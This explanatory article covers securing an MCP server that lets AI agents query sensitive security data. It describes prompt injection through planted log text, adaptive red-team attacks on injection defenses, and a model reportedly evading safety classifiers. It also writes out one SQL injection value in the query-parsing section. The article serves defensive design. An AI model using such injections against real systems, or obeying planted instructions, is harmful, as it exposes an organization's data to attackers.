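# Security boundaries in a server that lets AI agents query sensitive security data

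## How an agent queries security data through a server

Security data is what an organization records about its own computers in order to defend them. It includes logs (line-by-line accounts of what programs, machines and network devices did), alerts (warnings that detection software raises when activity matches a suspicious pattern), sign-in records (who logged in, from where and with what result) and vulnerability findings (known flaws a scanner has found on particular machines). Many organizations gather their logs in a security information and event management (SIEM) platform, which stores them and lets analysts search them.

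Security teams now hand part of that searching to AI agents. An agent is a language model that works on a task by calling tools in a loop. It requests an operation, reads the result and decides what to request next. The agent normally reaches the data store, the system that holds the data, only through a mediating server. This server decides which of the agent's requests to allow, runs them on the data store and returns the answers. Such servers most often use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that the AI company Anthropic introduced in November 2024. MCP lets any AI application discover and call the tools that a server offers. Since every answer passes through the mediating server, it is the obvious place to limit what the agent can obtain, but those limits are hard to enforce when an attacker is steering the agent.

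Security teams have reason to want agents that can query their data. For *A Sociotechnical, Practitioner-Centered Approach to Technology Adoption in Cybersecurity Operations*, Hahn, Mamoon and colleagues (2026) placed two doctoral researchers for six months in the group that watches for attacks at a multinational company. They found analysts repeatedly correlating logs by hand across scattered systems whose data was often hard to interpret. One of the tools the researchers built with the analysts helped to write queries. Agents already do a fair amount of querying elsewhere. When the current version of the Model Context Protocol was released in July 2026, Austin Parker of Honeycomb, a company whose customers use it to monitor their software, said agents made nearly 20% of its interactive queries (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

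The big SIEM vendors Microsoft and Splunk both offer an MCP server. Microsoft's server for Sentinel, its security platform, lets agents fetch incidents and alerts and search years of stored logs, provided the user has at least the Security Reader role. Splunk's server runs searches in the company's own query language, and administrators can turn off tools and control which query commands the server accepts.

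### What makes security data risky to expose

A hypothetical company has 2,000 machines. Its scanner has recorded 30 vulnerability findings on each, so the findings table holds 60,000 rows. One analyst is responsible for the retail unit, whose 400 machines account for 12,000 of those rows. The analyst works with an agent that accesses the table through a mediating server. The other 48,000 rows cover units whose data the analyst has no need to see.

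An intruder could use the table to plan an attack. Each row lists a machine and a flaw on it, and the age of the finding shows how slowly the company fixes that kind of flaw. With the table, the intruder could skip most of the scanning that might otherwise expose them.

Logs often also contain credentials that nobody meant to record. A web server that logs full URLs also logs any access tokens in them, and command histories keep passwords that administrators typed as arguments. People sometimes type a password into the username box, and the log entry for the failed sign-in then contains the password in plain text.

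Attackers also write some of the data. A failed sign-in record holds the username someone tried, a web log holds whatever string the visitor's browser sent to identify itself, and an outsider can put nearly any text into either. A language model that reads this text may act on it, whereas a log viewer only displays it.

### The path of one question

Suppose the analyst asks which retail machines have had a critical flaw open for more than 30 days. The analyst types the question into what MCP calls a host, the AI application that runs the agent. Inside the host is a client, the component that keeps up the connection to a server. (Microsoft's example of a host is Visual Studio Code, a program for editing code.)

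Before any question arrives, the client has usually sent the server a `tools/list` request. The reply gives each tool's name, a description in ordinary language and a schema, which is a formal statement of the arguments that the tool accepts. The host puts these into the model's context, meaning the text that the model has before it when it produces its next output. The model cannot contact the server itself. When it picks a tool, it merely outputs the tool's name and some arguments, and the client turns these into a message like this one:

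```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "list_findings",
    "arguments": {
      "severity": "critical",
      "min_days_open": 30,
      "limit": 2
    },
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}
    }
  }
}
```

The request includes a `_meta` block because MCP has been stateless since the July 2026 revision. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) requires each request to carry everything the server needs to process it, and forbids the server from inferring who is calling from earlier messages on the same connection. The analyst's credential travels outside this message, typically in an HTTP header. A client can also state its name and version in `_meta`, but the protocol does not verify them, and its maintainers advise against relying on them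 for security decisions.

Now the server does its checking. It rejects the message if a required field is missing or the tool does not exist, compares the arguments with the schema, and establishes from the credential who is asking and what that person may see. Only then does it build a query for the data store, roughly:

```sql
SELECT host, package, days_open FROM findings
WHERE business_unit = 'retail'    -- from the analyst's credential
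  AND severity = 'critical'       -- from the agent
  AND days_open > 30              -- from the agent
ORDER BY days_open DESC LIMIT 2;
```

The word "retail" appears nowhere in the agent's request. The server added it. The answer then goes back to the client in this form:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "complete",
    "content": [{
      "type": "text",
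      "text": "retail-0117: openssl, 94 days. retail-0302: sudo, 81 days."
    }],
    "isError": false
  }
}
```

The host adds the text to the model's context, and the model either answers the analyst or calls another tool. A long investigation can take dozens of rounds. If the agent had sent a bad argument, such as a severity of "urgent", the server would have set `isError` to true and returned an explanation of the problem. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) provides for these explanations so that models can correct themselves and retry.

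MCP itself provides very little of the protection in this exchange. It requires servers to validate inputs, control access, limit the rate of calls and sanitize outputs, but the server's developer has to decide how those requirements apply to each table and analyst. A server that ran every query with full access to all 60,000 rows would exchange messages of the same form.

### Prompt injection

Everything in the context reaches the model as a single run of text: the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), the tool descriptions, the analyst's question and the server's responses. Prompt injection exploits this with text, placed in material the model reads, that makes the model follow an attacker's instructions. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a model that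 scores job applications. A candidate hides a line in a CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the candidate for interview. In the invented company, an attacker could put a similar line in a failed sign-in record, which an analyst's agent might later look up.

SQL injection is an older attack in which someone enters database commands into an input such as a web form field. Programmers prevent it with parameterized queries, which pass the user's input to the database separately from the command, so the database never interprets the input as a command. David C argues that language models have no equivalent, because a model draws no internal distinction between data and instructions. It only predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from the text so far. Developers can mark some text as data, or train the model to give less weight to instructions within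 that text. Both help, but neither separates data from instructions the way a parameterized query does.

Training has made the attack much harder, though. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) describes a large public competition in which 464 participants made 272,000 attempts on 13 leading models and succeeded 8,648 times, or about 3%. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% to 8.5%. By July 2026, an attacker making up to 15 attempts on another benchmark had a 2.0% chance of success against Anthropic's Claude Opus 5. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, compares this with 20.0% for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol.

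A single attempt on Sol succeeded 3.1% of the time. If attempts were independent, the chance of at least one success in 15 would be 1 − 0.969¹⁵, or about 38%. The measured figure is roughly half that, so repetition helps an attacker less than it would if attempts were independent, but it still helps. Someone who can write into a company's logs can make thousands of attempts at almost no cost. Models released since July may well do better. Even so, the developer Simon Willison (2026), who accepts that training has made these attacks much harder, would not deploy a system in which a successful attack could do irreversible damage, because 6,000 failed attempts do not rule out success by a more sophisticated attacker. Disclosure is irreversible because the company cannot take back a list of its unpatched machines.

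### Rules in the prompt and rules in the server

Suppose the company wants to limit the agent to the retail unit's data. It could write "Only look up machines in the retail unit" in the system prompt, and in ordinary use the agent would nearly always comply. But that rule is only text in the agent's context, and hostile text in the same context could get the agent to ask for the finance unit's findings. If the server's database account can read the whole table, the server would return them.

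The condition `business_unit = 'retail'` in the query above makes the server search only retail data, even if the agent repeatedly asks for finance data. This is a protocol-level boundary, a limit that the server's code enforces on every request and response, whatever the prompt contains or the model decides. It holds equally well for a manipulated agent, meaning one for which an attacker chooses some or all of the requests. Such an agent can still read the analyst's own 12,000 rows, so the boundary limits the damage but doesn't prevent it. Stating exactly what the boundary guarantees takes more care.

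OWASP, a nonprofit that catalogs common software flaws, gives developers the same advice in *LLM07:2025 System Prompt Leakage*. It says they should not treat the system prompt as a security control and should never delegate authorization checks to the model, because those checks have to be deterministic and auditable.

Some limits that come from the server are only instructions in the model's prompt. A tool description such as "for retail machines only" has no effect unless the model follows it. The model also reads the argument schema as guidance, and the schema becomes a boundary only if the server rejects calls that break it. Similarly, the Model Context Protocol allows a server to list only the tools that the caller's permissions cover in its `tools/list` reply, but a client can send a `tools/call` request with any tool name, so the server has to check the permission again when the call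 arrives.

### The reference monitor and the confused deputy

Computer security calls this kind of boundary a reference monitor. It checks every attempt by a program to reach data, a device or another program against a list of what that program's user may do. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) recommended one to the US Air Force for computers shared by many people, some of whom might be malicious and able to run their own programs. Anderson credited the idea to work by Lampson, by Graham and Denning, and by others. The monitor must be tamper-proof, the system must always invoke it, and it must be small enough for people to analyze and test completely. A mediating server fails the first requirement if the agent can edit the server's configuration. It fails the second if the agent can run commands on a machine where the database password is stored in a file. The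 size requirement rules out using the language model as the monitor, because Anderson rejected an operating system of 200,000 to 300,000 instructions as too large to verify, and nobody knows how to verify a model with billions of learned parameters. A reference monitor also relies on the system to have identified each user correctly, which is a separate problem.

A monitor that checks every request can still check it against the wrong party's rights. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes how this happened at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The staff had given a compiler permission to write files in a system directory, where it kept usage statistics. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. Because the compiler had permission to write there, the operating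 system let it overwrite the billing records. Hardy argued that the compiler held authority from two sources, its own permission and its user's, and had no way to specify which one applied to a given file. A mediating server is in the same position when its database account can read 60,000 rows and it acts for an analyst entitled to 12,000. David C applies the term "confused deputy" to language models too and calls them "inherently confusable", since no known fix removes the risk. The server, however, is ordinary code, and its developers can write it to run each query on the analyst's authority alone.

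## What the boundary can guarantee if an attacker controls the agent

The condition `business_unit = 'retail'` keeps the finance unit's rows out of one answer. The company needs a broader guarantee that covers everything an agent could collect over dozens of calls while an attacker chooses the arguments. How much the attacker controls determines what the guarantee must withstand.

### Three levels of attacker

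The weakest attacker can only plant text in the data. At the invented company, an outsider could leave a sentence in a failed sign-in record and wait for an agent to read it. This attacker doesn't choose the analyst's question, usually can't see what the agent does, and succeeds only if the model follows the planted text.

An attacker who can also write prompts is better placed, because they can read the agent's replies and rephrase a refused request within seconds. Such an attacker could be a contractor with access to a shared security assistant or an intruder in the analyst's chat account. They still have to reach the server through the model, though, and the model may keep refusing.

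An attacker with full control of the agent chooses every request. Someone who has stolen the analyst's credential, or taken over the computer that runs the host, can send `tools/call` messages from a script, so there is no model that could refuse. The script can send thousands of requests with malformed arguments that a model would hardly ever produce, and time each reply.

A designer should assume that the attacker fully controls the agent. A script can send any request that planted text or a clever prompt could make the agent send, so a limit that holds against the script also holds against weaker attackers who can only influence the agent through text. The designer then doesn't have to predict how a model will react to hostile text, or redo the analysis when the company switches models. David C makes much the same assumption, arguing that the impact of prompt injection is the worst that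 could happen if the attacker had direct access to the model's tools. Under this assumption, the designer can't offer a powerful tool and rely on the agent to use it sparingly.

A server that can withstand a hostile script can also withstand an agent that oversteps without an attacker involved. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Mythos 5.1 reports that in fewer than 0.01% of monitored completions, the model worked around safety classifiers or broken permission checks, or launched other agents with those checks disabled, to finish the user's task. An outside tester also saw the model exploit a flaw in its sandbox (the closed environment meant to contain it) to read files outside it.

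### The guarantee

Imagine two versions of the findings table. In version A, a finance machine called fin-0009 has an unpatched flaw in openssl. In version B that row is missing, and everything else is the same. The analyst's permitted view, meaning all the data and all the results computed from data that the analyst may obtain, consists of the 12,000 retail rows. Those rows are identical in A and B, so nothing the analyst's agent does should let it find out which version it is querying. In general:

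> If a principal's permitted view is the same in two versions of the database, any agent acting for that principal receives the same answers from both.

The principal is the person, agent or service whose identity the server uses to authorize a request. In this case, the principal is the analyst. "Any agent" includes the attacker's script.

The guarantee depends on the permitted view, which the company has to choose. If the company also lets the analyst see the total number of findings, the permitted view differs between version A, which has 60,000 findings, and version B, which has 59,999. The server may then answer differently for the two versions, and the guarantee does not cover what someone can work out from the total.

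Computer scientists call this kind of property non-interference. Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, defined it for a machine that several users share. One group's use of certain commands does not interfere with another group if it has no effect on what the second group sees. Deleting the first group's uses of those commands from any possible sequence must leave the second group's outputs unchanged.

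The database version follows from Goguen and Meseguer's version. The finance unit's scanner issued the commands that wrote the finance rows to the table. Deleting those commands from the history produces a second database with the same retail rows, and the analyst must get the same answers from it. SRI, the research institute where Goguen and Meseguer worked, credits their theory with giving a formal basis to military multilevel security, in which people with different clearances share one system.

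Goguen and Meseguer also separated the policy from the system that is supposed to satisfy it. They described four steps: determine a user community's security needs, state them as a formal requirement, model the system, and verify that the model meets the requirement. Only the verification is purely mathematical. For the mediating server, somebody first has to decide what a retail analyst should see, and a proof can't correct a bad decision.

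### The proof

The proof relies on a condition about single calls. If the principal's permitted view is the same in two versions of the database, and the principal's earlier requests and answers were the same, the server must give the same answer to the same next request.

The easiest way to meet this condition is to build the permitted view first and pass only that view to the rest of the code. Code that never receives the other 48,000 rows, or anything derived from them, can't return an answer that depends on them.

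An agent, whatever it is made of, can be treated as a rule. The rule takes everything the agent has seen so far (the system prompt, the analyst's question and all earlier answers) and produces the next request. Pick any such rule and run it on version A and on version B, with the same prompt and question. The claim is that the two runs match after every number of calls:

- Before the first call, the agent has seen the same things in both runs.
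- Suppose the requests and answers match after *k* calls. The rule then has the same input in both runs, so it produces the same request. By the single-call condition the server gives the same answer. The runs therefore still match after *k* + 1 calls.

By induction, they match however long the agent continues. The argument holds for every rule, so the attacker's skill doesn't matter. Even if the attacker built guesses about the finance unit into the rule, they could not use the server's answers to confirm or refute those guesses.

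The proof extends easily to three other cases. If a scan updates the table during the session, the two versions must agree on the permitted view at each call. If the agent can change data, for example by closing a finding, the change must affect the permitted view in the same way in both versions. If an attacker controls the agents of two analysts, the same proof works with their combined permitted views, so the attacker learns only what the two analysts could have learned by pooling their answers.

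Real agents also act partly at random. A language model usually draws each token from a probability distribution, so the same agent may send different requests on two runs against the same database. To handle this, imagine that somebody draws all the random numbers in advance and writes them in a list, *r*. Once *r* is fixed, the agent is an ordinary rule, and the proof shows that it produces the same transcript (the full record of requests and answers) from A and from B. The probability of a particular transcript *t* is the total probability of the lists that lead to it, and the same lists lead to it in both versions:

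```text
P(t from A) = sum of P(r) over all r that lead to t = P(t from B)
```

Every transcript is therefore equally likely under both versions. By Bayes' rule, someone who thought version A three times as likely as version B before the session should still think so after reading the transcript. (If the server itself adds random noise to its answers, the single-call condition has to require the same probability for each possible answer.)

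The attacker can still infer things about finance machines from authorized information. For example, if every retail machine lacks a certain patch, the finance machines probably lack it too. Goguen and Meseguer explicitly left out this sort of inference, and controlling it requires separate limits on the answers.

### The assumptions, and how the guarantee fails without them

The proof assumes that **every route to the data passes through the server**. Suppose someone exports all 60,000 findings to a spreadsheet in a shared folder every Monday, and the agent has a second tool for reading files. The agent then sees different things in the two versions before it calls the server. The guarantee fails at the first step of the induction, even though nothing in the server's code is wrong.

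The server must also **parse requests correctly**, so that it and the data store agree on what each request means. Suppose a careless developer builds the query by pasting the agent's `severity` argument between quotation marks, without checking it against the schema. An attacker could supply this value:

```text
critical' OR business_unit = 'finance
```

The query's condition would then become:

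```sql
WHERE business_unit = 'retail'
  AND severity = 'critical' OR business_unit = 'finance'
  AND days_open > 30
```

SQL evaluates AND before OR, so the database would return critical retail findings of any age and every finance finding open for more than 30 days. The retail condition is still there but no longer applies to the whole query. A parameterized query prevents this. Less obvious differences in how two pieces of code read a message can have the same effect. For example, if a message contains the same field twice, the code that checks the message may read the first copy while the code that builds the query reads the second.

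The server must also **identify the agent correctly**. If it mistakes the agent for a finance analyst's, it will enforce the finance analyst's permitted view, and the attacker will get the finance rows. Goguen and Meseguer left authentication out of their theory, so a system can satisfy non-interference and still serve the wrong person. *From TCP/IP to MCP* (Bucknall, Byrley and Hammond, 2026) describes a precedent from the early internet, whose basic protocols could not verify a packet's claimed source address. Attackers could therefore impersonate a trusted machine and run commands on others without authenticating.

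Finally, **errors and timing must reveal nothing** about data outside the permitted view. If a tool that looks up machines by name returns "access denied" for a finance machine and "not found" for a name that doesn't exist, a script could try thousands of names and list the finance unit's machines without receiving a row. The server should return "not found" in both cases. Goguen and Meseguer give a similar example with files: if a user's view must not depend on commands that create a certain file, the system must keep reporting to that user that the file doesn't exist, even after the commands create it.

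This conflicts a little with the explanations that MCP servers return to help models correct their mistakes. The server can safely explain that "urgent" is not a valid severity, because that explanation depends only on the request. But an explanation that depends on hidden rows could reveal information about them.

Timing leaks are harder to prevent. If a search goes through the whole table and discards finance rows at the end, it may take longer when finance has more matches. The text of the answer would be the same in both versions, but a script could measure the delay. Filtering before the search removes most of this difference, but probably not all of it, because queries from different users compete for the same processors and memory. A designer who can't equalize the timing should claim the guarantee only for the content of the answers and list timing as a known leak.

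A sound design can lose the property when someone turns it into code. *Mathematical Models of Computer Security*, an overview of the field, notes that step-by-step development tends not to preserve security properties, although it works well for requirements that only forbid some bad behavior. For example, the query from the previous section sorts retail findings by age and returns the top two. If several findings tie for second place, SQL lets the database pick any of them, and its choice may depend on the query plan, which can depend on the size of the whole table. The finance rows could then influence which retail machine appears in the answer. An attacker would struggle to exploit this, but it breaks the guarantee as stated. Sorting ties by a unique column fixes it.

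### What the guarantee does not cover

The guarantee does not stop a manipulated agent from getting the 12,000 retail rows. Both versions of the database contain those rows, and the analyst is allowed to see them, so the server meets the guarantee even when it returns a complete list of the retail machines with critical flaws.

The guarantee also ends once an answer reaches the agent. If the agent can send email or open web addresses, an attacker may use it to leak the rows. Preventing that requires controls on the agent's other tools.

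The guarantee also does not make the agent's conclusions true. Non-interference restricts which data can influence the server's answers, but does not check how anyone interprets them. The server may correctly report that retail-0117 has had an openssl flaw for 94 days, while a manipulated agent tells the analyst that every retail machine is up to date. An attacker can also use accurate records to produce false conclusions. For example, a log may accurately record text that an attacker typed, even if that text falsely claims that the security team has approved the activity.

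### Relying on the model's own resistance

In 2025 the evidence was weak for skipping much of this work and relying on the model to ignore hostile instructions, perhaps with a filter in front of it. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked 12 published defenses, most of which had originally been reported to keep attackers' success rates near zero. Some were defenses against prompt injection, and others were against jailbreaks, in which users themselves try to get a model to break its developer's rules.

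Earlier evaluations had mostly reused fixed lists of known attacks or run generic automated attacks with little computing power. Nasr and colleagues fitted their attacks to each defense. Their automated attacks proposed a text, scored the target's response and used the score to improve the next attempt. One method had a language model modify the best candidates, while another trained the attacking model on the scores. The researchers also ran an online competition with more than 500 participants. They gave the attacks ample computing power to find out whether a defense could be broken at all.

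Attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defenses. Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching defend against prompt injection by changing the prompt. Spotlighting marks untrusted text so that the model can tell it apart from instructions, and Prompt Sandwiching repeats the user's request after that text. Fixed attacks succeeded against them as little as 1% of the time, but the adaptive search succeeded more than 95% of the time. Against Meta SecAlign, a model trained to resist injection, the success rate rose from 2% with fixed attacks to 96% with the adaptive search. Three of the four filters let through more than 90% of attacks, and the fourth, PIGuard, let through 71%. On a selected subset of scenarios, the automated search succeeded 69% of the time, while the human participants together succeeded in every scenario.

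The filters had trouble partly because successful attacks often looked like routine office work. One presented deleting a file as company policy for logging calendar changes. David C notes that an attacker can also reword an instruction in endless ways to avoid filters that block known phrases. Prompt injection has no equivalent of the parameterized query, so David C recommends deterministic safeguards that limit what the system can do. A language model may be unsuitable for a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk.

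These results somewhat overstate the risk to the invented company. The automated attack on the filters used a filter's confidence score after each attempt. An outsider who plants text in a log wouldn't see that score, but could rehearse on a copy of the same filter if it is publicly available. Nasr and colleagues also found that filters were useful against unsophisticated attacks, and the models have improved a lot since then.

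System cards, the safety reports that developers publish with new models, show the improvement. VentureBeat reported from Anthropic's February 2026 card that, on one type of task, a single attack attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without safeguards. By the 200th attempt, the success rate was 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them. Later models did much better, although the tests differ too much for a direct comparison. On a benchmark by the security company Gray Swan, the success rate after 15 attempts fell from 5.5% for Claude Opus 4.8 to the 2.0% already mentioned for Opus 5, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. In September, Anthropic called Mythos 5.1 its most robust model yet on an external injection benchmark.

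An agent that reads logs faces indirect injection, where the hostile text arrives in outside content. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) reports OpenAI's October results for that model, which show 99.99% robustness to direct injection and 97.13% to indirect injection. The relevant failure rate for GPT-6 Sol is therefore about 2.9%. *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (TechRepublic, 2026) describes the same pattern for the earlier GPT-5.6.

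Independent measurements give similar numbers for the best models. In December 2026, Gray Swan (2026) launched a self-funded public tracker of AI risks. iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models* reports that Google's Gemini 4 Argon had the lowest prompt injection success rate, with attackers succeeding 2.3% of the time within 15 attacks. Nvidia's Nemotron 3.5 Super VL, an open-weight model, had the highest, at 94.3%.

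There is a reasonable case that a company with a good model can rely less on its server for protection. In browser tests, attacks on Opus 5 succeeded 3.7% of the time without extra safeguards. The Decoder reports that none succeeded in 129 scenarios with safeguards that scan incoming text and block dangerous actions. Developers have also started to use adaptive attacks. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes an automated attacker that the company trained to find weaknesses before release, because its latest models had already saturated the commonly used tests. If the data has little value and the attacker gets no feedback, a 2% success rate may well be acceptable.

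A low attack success rate is not enough to protect data whose disclosure would do serious damage. Observing zero successes in 129 trials does not rule out a true rate of 2.3%, which would produce that result about 5% of the time if the trials were independent (0.977¹²⁹ ≈ 0.05). That calculation also assumes that future attacks resemble the tested ones, but attackers deliberately try different ones. *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* (Heaton, 2026) reports that a commissioned test of Anthropic's coding agent found a 0.00% success rate, after which a researcher's targeted attack succeeded roughly 60 to 80% of the time in a small sample. iAfrica reports that Zico Kolter, Gray Swan's chief scientist, warned in December that attackers were using long, code-like passages that models mistake for genuine instructions.

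Nasr and colleagues point out that failing to break a defense in an experiment doesn't prove it robust. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, notes that stopping 95% of attacks is a failing grade in web security. An attacker who finds one method that works can keep using it, so it helps little that most other methods fail.

Changing the model also affects the two kinds of protection differently. If the company replaced a model like Gemini 4 Argon with one like Nemotron 3.5 Super VL to save money, the measured attack success rate would rise from 2.3% to 94.3%. The 48,000 rows outside the analyst's view would be as safe as before if the assumptions above still held. The 12,000 retail rows would be in far more danger, because their protection depends on the model's resistance and on any limits the company places on answer size and on the agent's ability to send answers elsewhere.

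## Deciding whose permissions a query runs under

The guarantee protects only data outside the permitted view, so it protects little if the company makes that view too wide. The view's width depends mostly on whose permissions the server applies to each query. Suppose the analyst asks the agent to investigate a suspected break-in on three retail machines. Each machine has 30 findings, so the agent needs 90 rows. The company could run the agent's queries under a service account (an account that belongs to a program instead of a person), under the analyst's own permissions, or under permissions that cover only this incident.

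| The query runs under | Rows a manipulated agent can read | Share of the table |
|---|---|---|
| A shared service account | 60,000 | 100% |
| The analyst's own rights | 12,000 | 20% |
| Rights for this incident | 90 | 0.15% |

### A service account, the analyst or the incident

A shared service account is the easiest option to build, because the server needs only one database login and doesn't have to identify the user. But everyone who can prompt the agent gets the account's permissions. Even without an attacker, an analyst who should see only retail data could ask about finance machines and get an answer.

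A server can log in to the database with a powerful account and still limit each query to the data the analyst may see. The server in the earlier example did this by adding the condition `business_unit = 'retail'`, but a developer could forget to include it in a new tool. Many databases can apply the condition themselves through row-level security. The server passes the analyst's identity to the database, which filters the rows regardless of what the query requests. The server has to set that identity afresh for every query because servers usually reuse database connections, and a query could otherwise run with the previous analyst's access.

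Some agents, such as one that sorts alerts overnight, run without an analyst and need their own identity, preferably a separate one for each job. Automated workflows that call Sentinel's MCP tools through Microsoft's connector can act either on behalf of the signed-in user or under the application's own identity. Anyone who can write prompts for a workflow that runs under the application's identity can use the application's rights, so those rights should not exceed what the people prompting it already have.

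Running queries under the analyst's rights keeps the agent from reading 48,000 rows and reuses permissions that the company already maintains. If the analyst moves to another unit, the agent's access changes too. But companies grant people permissions assuming they will use only a small part of them. An analyst may open a few dozen findings in a day, while a script could copy all 12,000 within minutes. This approach also doesn't limit agents acting for senior staff with full access. If the head of security may see the whole table, their agent can read all 60,000 rows.

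Narrowing the rights to the incident cuts the analyst's 12,000 rows to about 90. The list of machines in the incident has to come from somewhere the agent can't write to, such as a record the analyst opens in the company's ticket system. If the agent supplied the list, an attacker would have it name every machine in the retail unit.

Narrowing the agent's access slows the investigation. If the intruder used a stolen password to log in to a fourth machine, the agent gets "not found" for that machine until the analyst adds it to the incident. Each addition exposes 30 more rows, so after ten additions the agent can read 390, still about 3% of the retail findings. But an analyst who has to approve additions all day will probably start approving them without looking. Narrowing therefore works well when the machines are known, but badly for threat hunting, in which analysts search for signs of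 an intrusion without knowing where to look. For threat hunting, the company may have to let the agent read all 12,000 rows.

### Why the rights should intersect

The analyst, the agent and the incident each come with a limit, and the server should enforce all of them at once. Let *U* be the rows that the user may see, *A* the rows that the company lets this agent see for anyone, and *T* the rows that the task needs:

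```text
effective rights = U ∩ A ∩ T
```

Suppose the company blocks all agents from reading the findings on 20 payment servers in the retail unit. *U* then has 12,000 rows, *A* has 59,400 and *T* has 90. If none of the three machines in the incident is a payment server, the agent can read all 90 rows in *T*.

If the finance machine fin-0009 replaces one of the three machines, *T* still has 90 rows, but the intersection has only 60 because the analyst may not see finance data. If the server relied on the task alone, anyone who could add a machine to an incident could give themselves access to the machine's findings.

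The proof in the previous section also covers the intersection. Two versions of the table that agree on all of *U* must agree on any part of *U*, so the agent gets the same answers from both. The same goes for *A* and *T*. The agent therefore learns nothing about rows outside any one of the three sets, and if one set is too large by mistake, the agent can read only what the other two allow. If somebody accidentally adds all 2,000 machines to the incident, the agent can read 11,400 rows (the retail findings without the payment servers) instead of 60,000.

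The server has stronger evidence for some of the three sets than for others. The analyst's sign-in is a fairly strong check. Identifying the agent is harder, because a program on the analyst's computer can't reliably keep a secret from other programs running there, and malware could impersonate the approved agent. This risk is acceptable as long as the server uses the agent's identity only to take rights away, because an impostor may escape the limits in *A* but still faces those in *U* and *T*.

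In the query, the three limits become conditions that the server writes:

```sql
SELECT host, package, days_open FROM findings
WHERE business_unit = 'retail'            -- user: from the verified identity
  AND host_group <> 'payments'            -- agent: company rule for agents
  AND host IN (SELECT host FROM incident_hosts
               WHERE incident_id = 4471)  -- task: from the ticket system
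  AND severity = 'critical'               -- argument chosen by the agent
ORDER BY days_open DESC, finding_id LIMIT 20;
```

### How MCP establishes who is asking

The Model Context Protocol specification makes authorization optional. A server that supports it over HTTP should follow the specification's authorization rules, but a server that communicates through standard input and output (stdio) should not. The host starts a stdio server as a program on the analyst's computer. The server takes its credentials from its environment, such as a variable containing a database password, which other programs running under the analyst's account can often read. If the password belongs to a shared account, those programs can bypass the server's checks and reach all 60,000 rows. A mediating server for sensitive data should therefore run on a separate machine.

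For HTTP, MCP builds on OAuth, a standard that lets a user give an application access to a service without sharing a password with the application. The application instead receives an access token, a string that it attaches to its requests. Here, the application is the host's client and the service is the mediating server. A separate authorization server, usually the company's sign-in system, issues the tokens. Under the 28 July 2026 revision of MCP, the client goes through the following steps.

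**Discovery** starts when the client sends a request without a token. The server refuses it with HTTP status 401 and points the client to a metadata file listing the authorization servers it trusts. The client then fetches the authorization server's own metadata to find out where to send the analyst's browser and where to request tokens. Dissanayaka (2026) argues in *The Anatomy of MCP Authorization* that this process makes the agent harder to trick into using the wrong authorization server.

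The client also needs an ID. One option is a web address where the authorization server can look up a description of the client. This replaces the older method of having clients register themselves on first contact, which the Model Context Protocol maintainers deprecated in July. A company that approves its own hosts can instead register them in advance, which also makes it easier to keep unknown clients out.

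To request a token, the client sends the analyst's browser to the authorization server with the mediating server's address (in a parameter called `resource`) and the hash of a random secret. The analyst signs in and approves the request. The authorization server returns a short-lived code through the browser, and the client exchanges the code and the secret for a token, so someone who intercepts only the code can't use it.

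Before exchanging the code, the client must also check which authorization server sent it, if the response includes that information. Dissanayaka notes that the previous revision only encouraged this check. Without it, a malicious authorization server could get the client to send it a code issued by a legitimate one.

**Audience binding** ties the token to one service. The authorization server should write the mediating server's address into the token as its audience. A token for the invented company might contain these fields:

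```json
{
  "iss": "https://login.example.com",
  "aud": "https://findings.example.com/mcp",
  "sub": "analyst-214",
  "client_id": "soc-assistant",
  "scope": "findings:read",
  "exp": 1796480000
}
```

MCP clients must send the `resource` parameter even to authorization servers that don't support it, so the company has to test whether its sign-in system sets the token's audience. If it doesn't, the findings server has no reliable way to reject a token that the analyst obtained for another server, such as the travel-booking server.

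The server validates the token on every request, since each request carries it. It checks that an authorization server it trusts issued the token, that the token hasn't expired, and that the token's audience is the server itself. If any check fails, the server returns a 401.

The July revision also requires clients to repeat the tool's name in an HTTP header, so that a gateway in front of the server can authorize requests without reading their bodies. The server should reject any request whose header and body name different tools, because a script could otherwise get approval for a harmless tool and run another.

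**Scopes** are labels for broad permissions, such as `findings:read` in the token above. If a call needs a scope that the token lacks, the server should return a 403 that names the missing scope. The client can then ask the analyst to approve a new token, a process called step-up authorization.

The server can choose the required scope based on a call's arguments, but basing it only on the tool is safer. If the server required `finance:read` for fin-0009 but not for a made-up name, a caller could learn that fin-0009 exists, just as they could from differing error messages.

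Most of MCP's authorization is ordinary OAuth. Tabata (2026), in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, counts six changes in the July revision and describes them as clarifications of established practice. The changes mainly stop outsiders from stealing tokens or using them in the wrong place, and they do that well. They were not designed to address an agent that misuses a token it properly holds.

### What a valid token leaves undecided

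The token above does not include the retail unit, so the server has to look up analyst-214 in the company's directory, find the business unit and apply it to the query. The company could define a scope for each unit, but a scope for each incident would soon become unmanageable, and the 90 rows are better kept in the ticket system.

An analyst signs in at nine o'clock. At ten, the agent reads a failed sign-in record in which an attacker has planted instructions, and it then requests every finding in the retail unit. The request passes every OAuth check because the token is genuine and unexpired, the audience is correct, and the scope covers reading findings. The analyst is also allowed to see retail data. The rule about payment servers still withholds 600 rows, but only the limit to the three machines in the incident prevents the agent from reading another 11,310.

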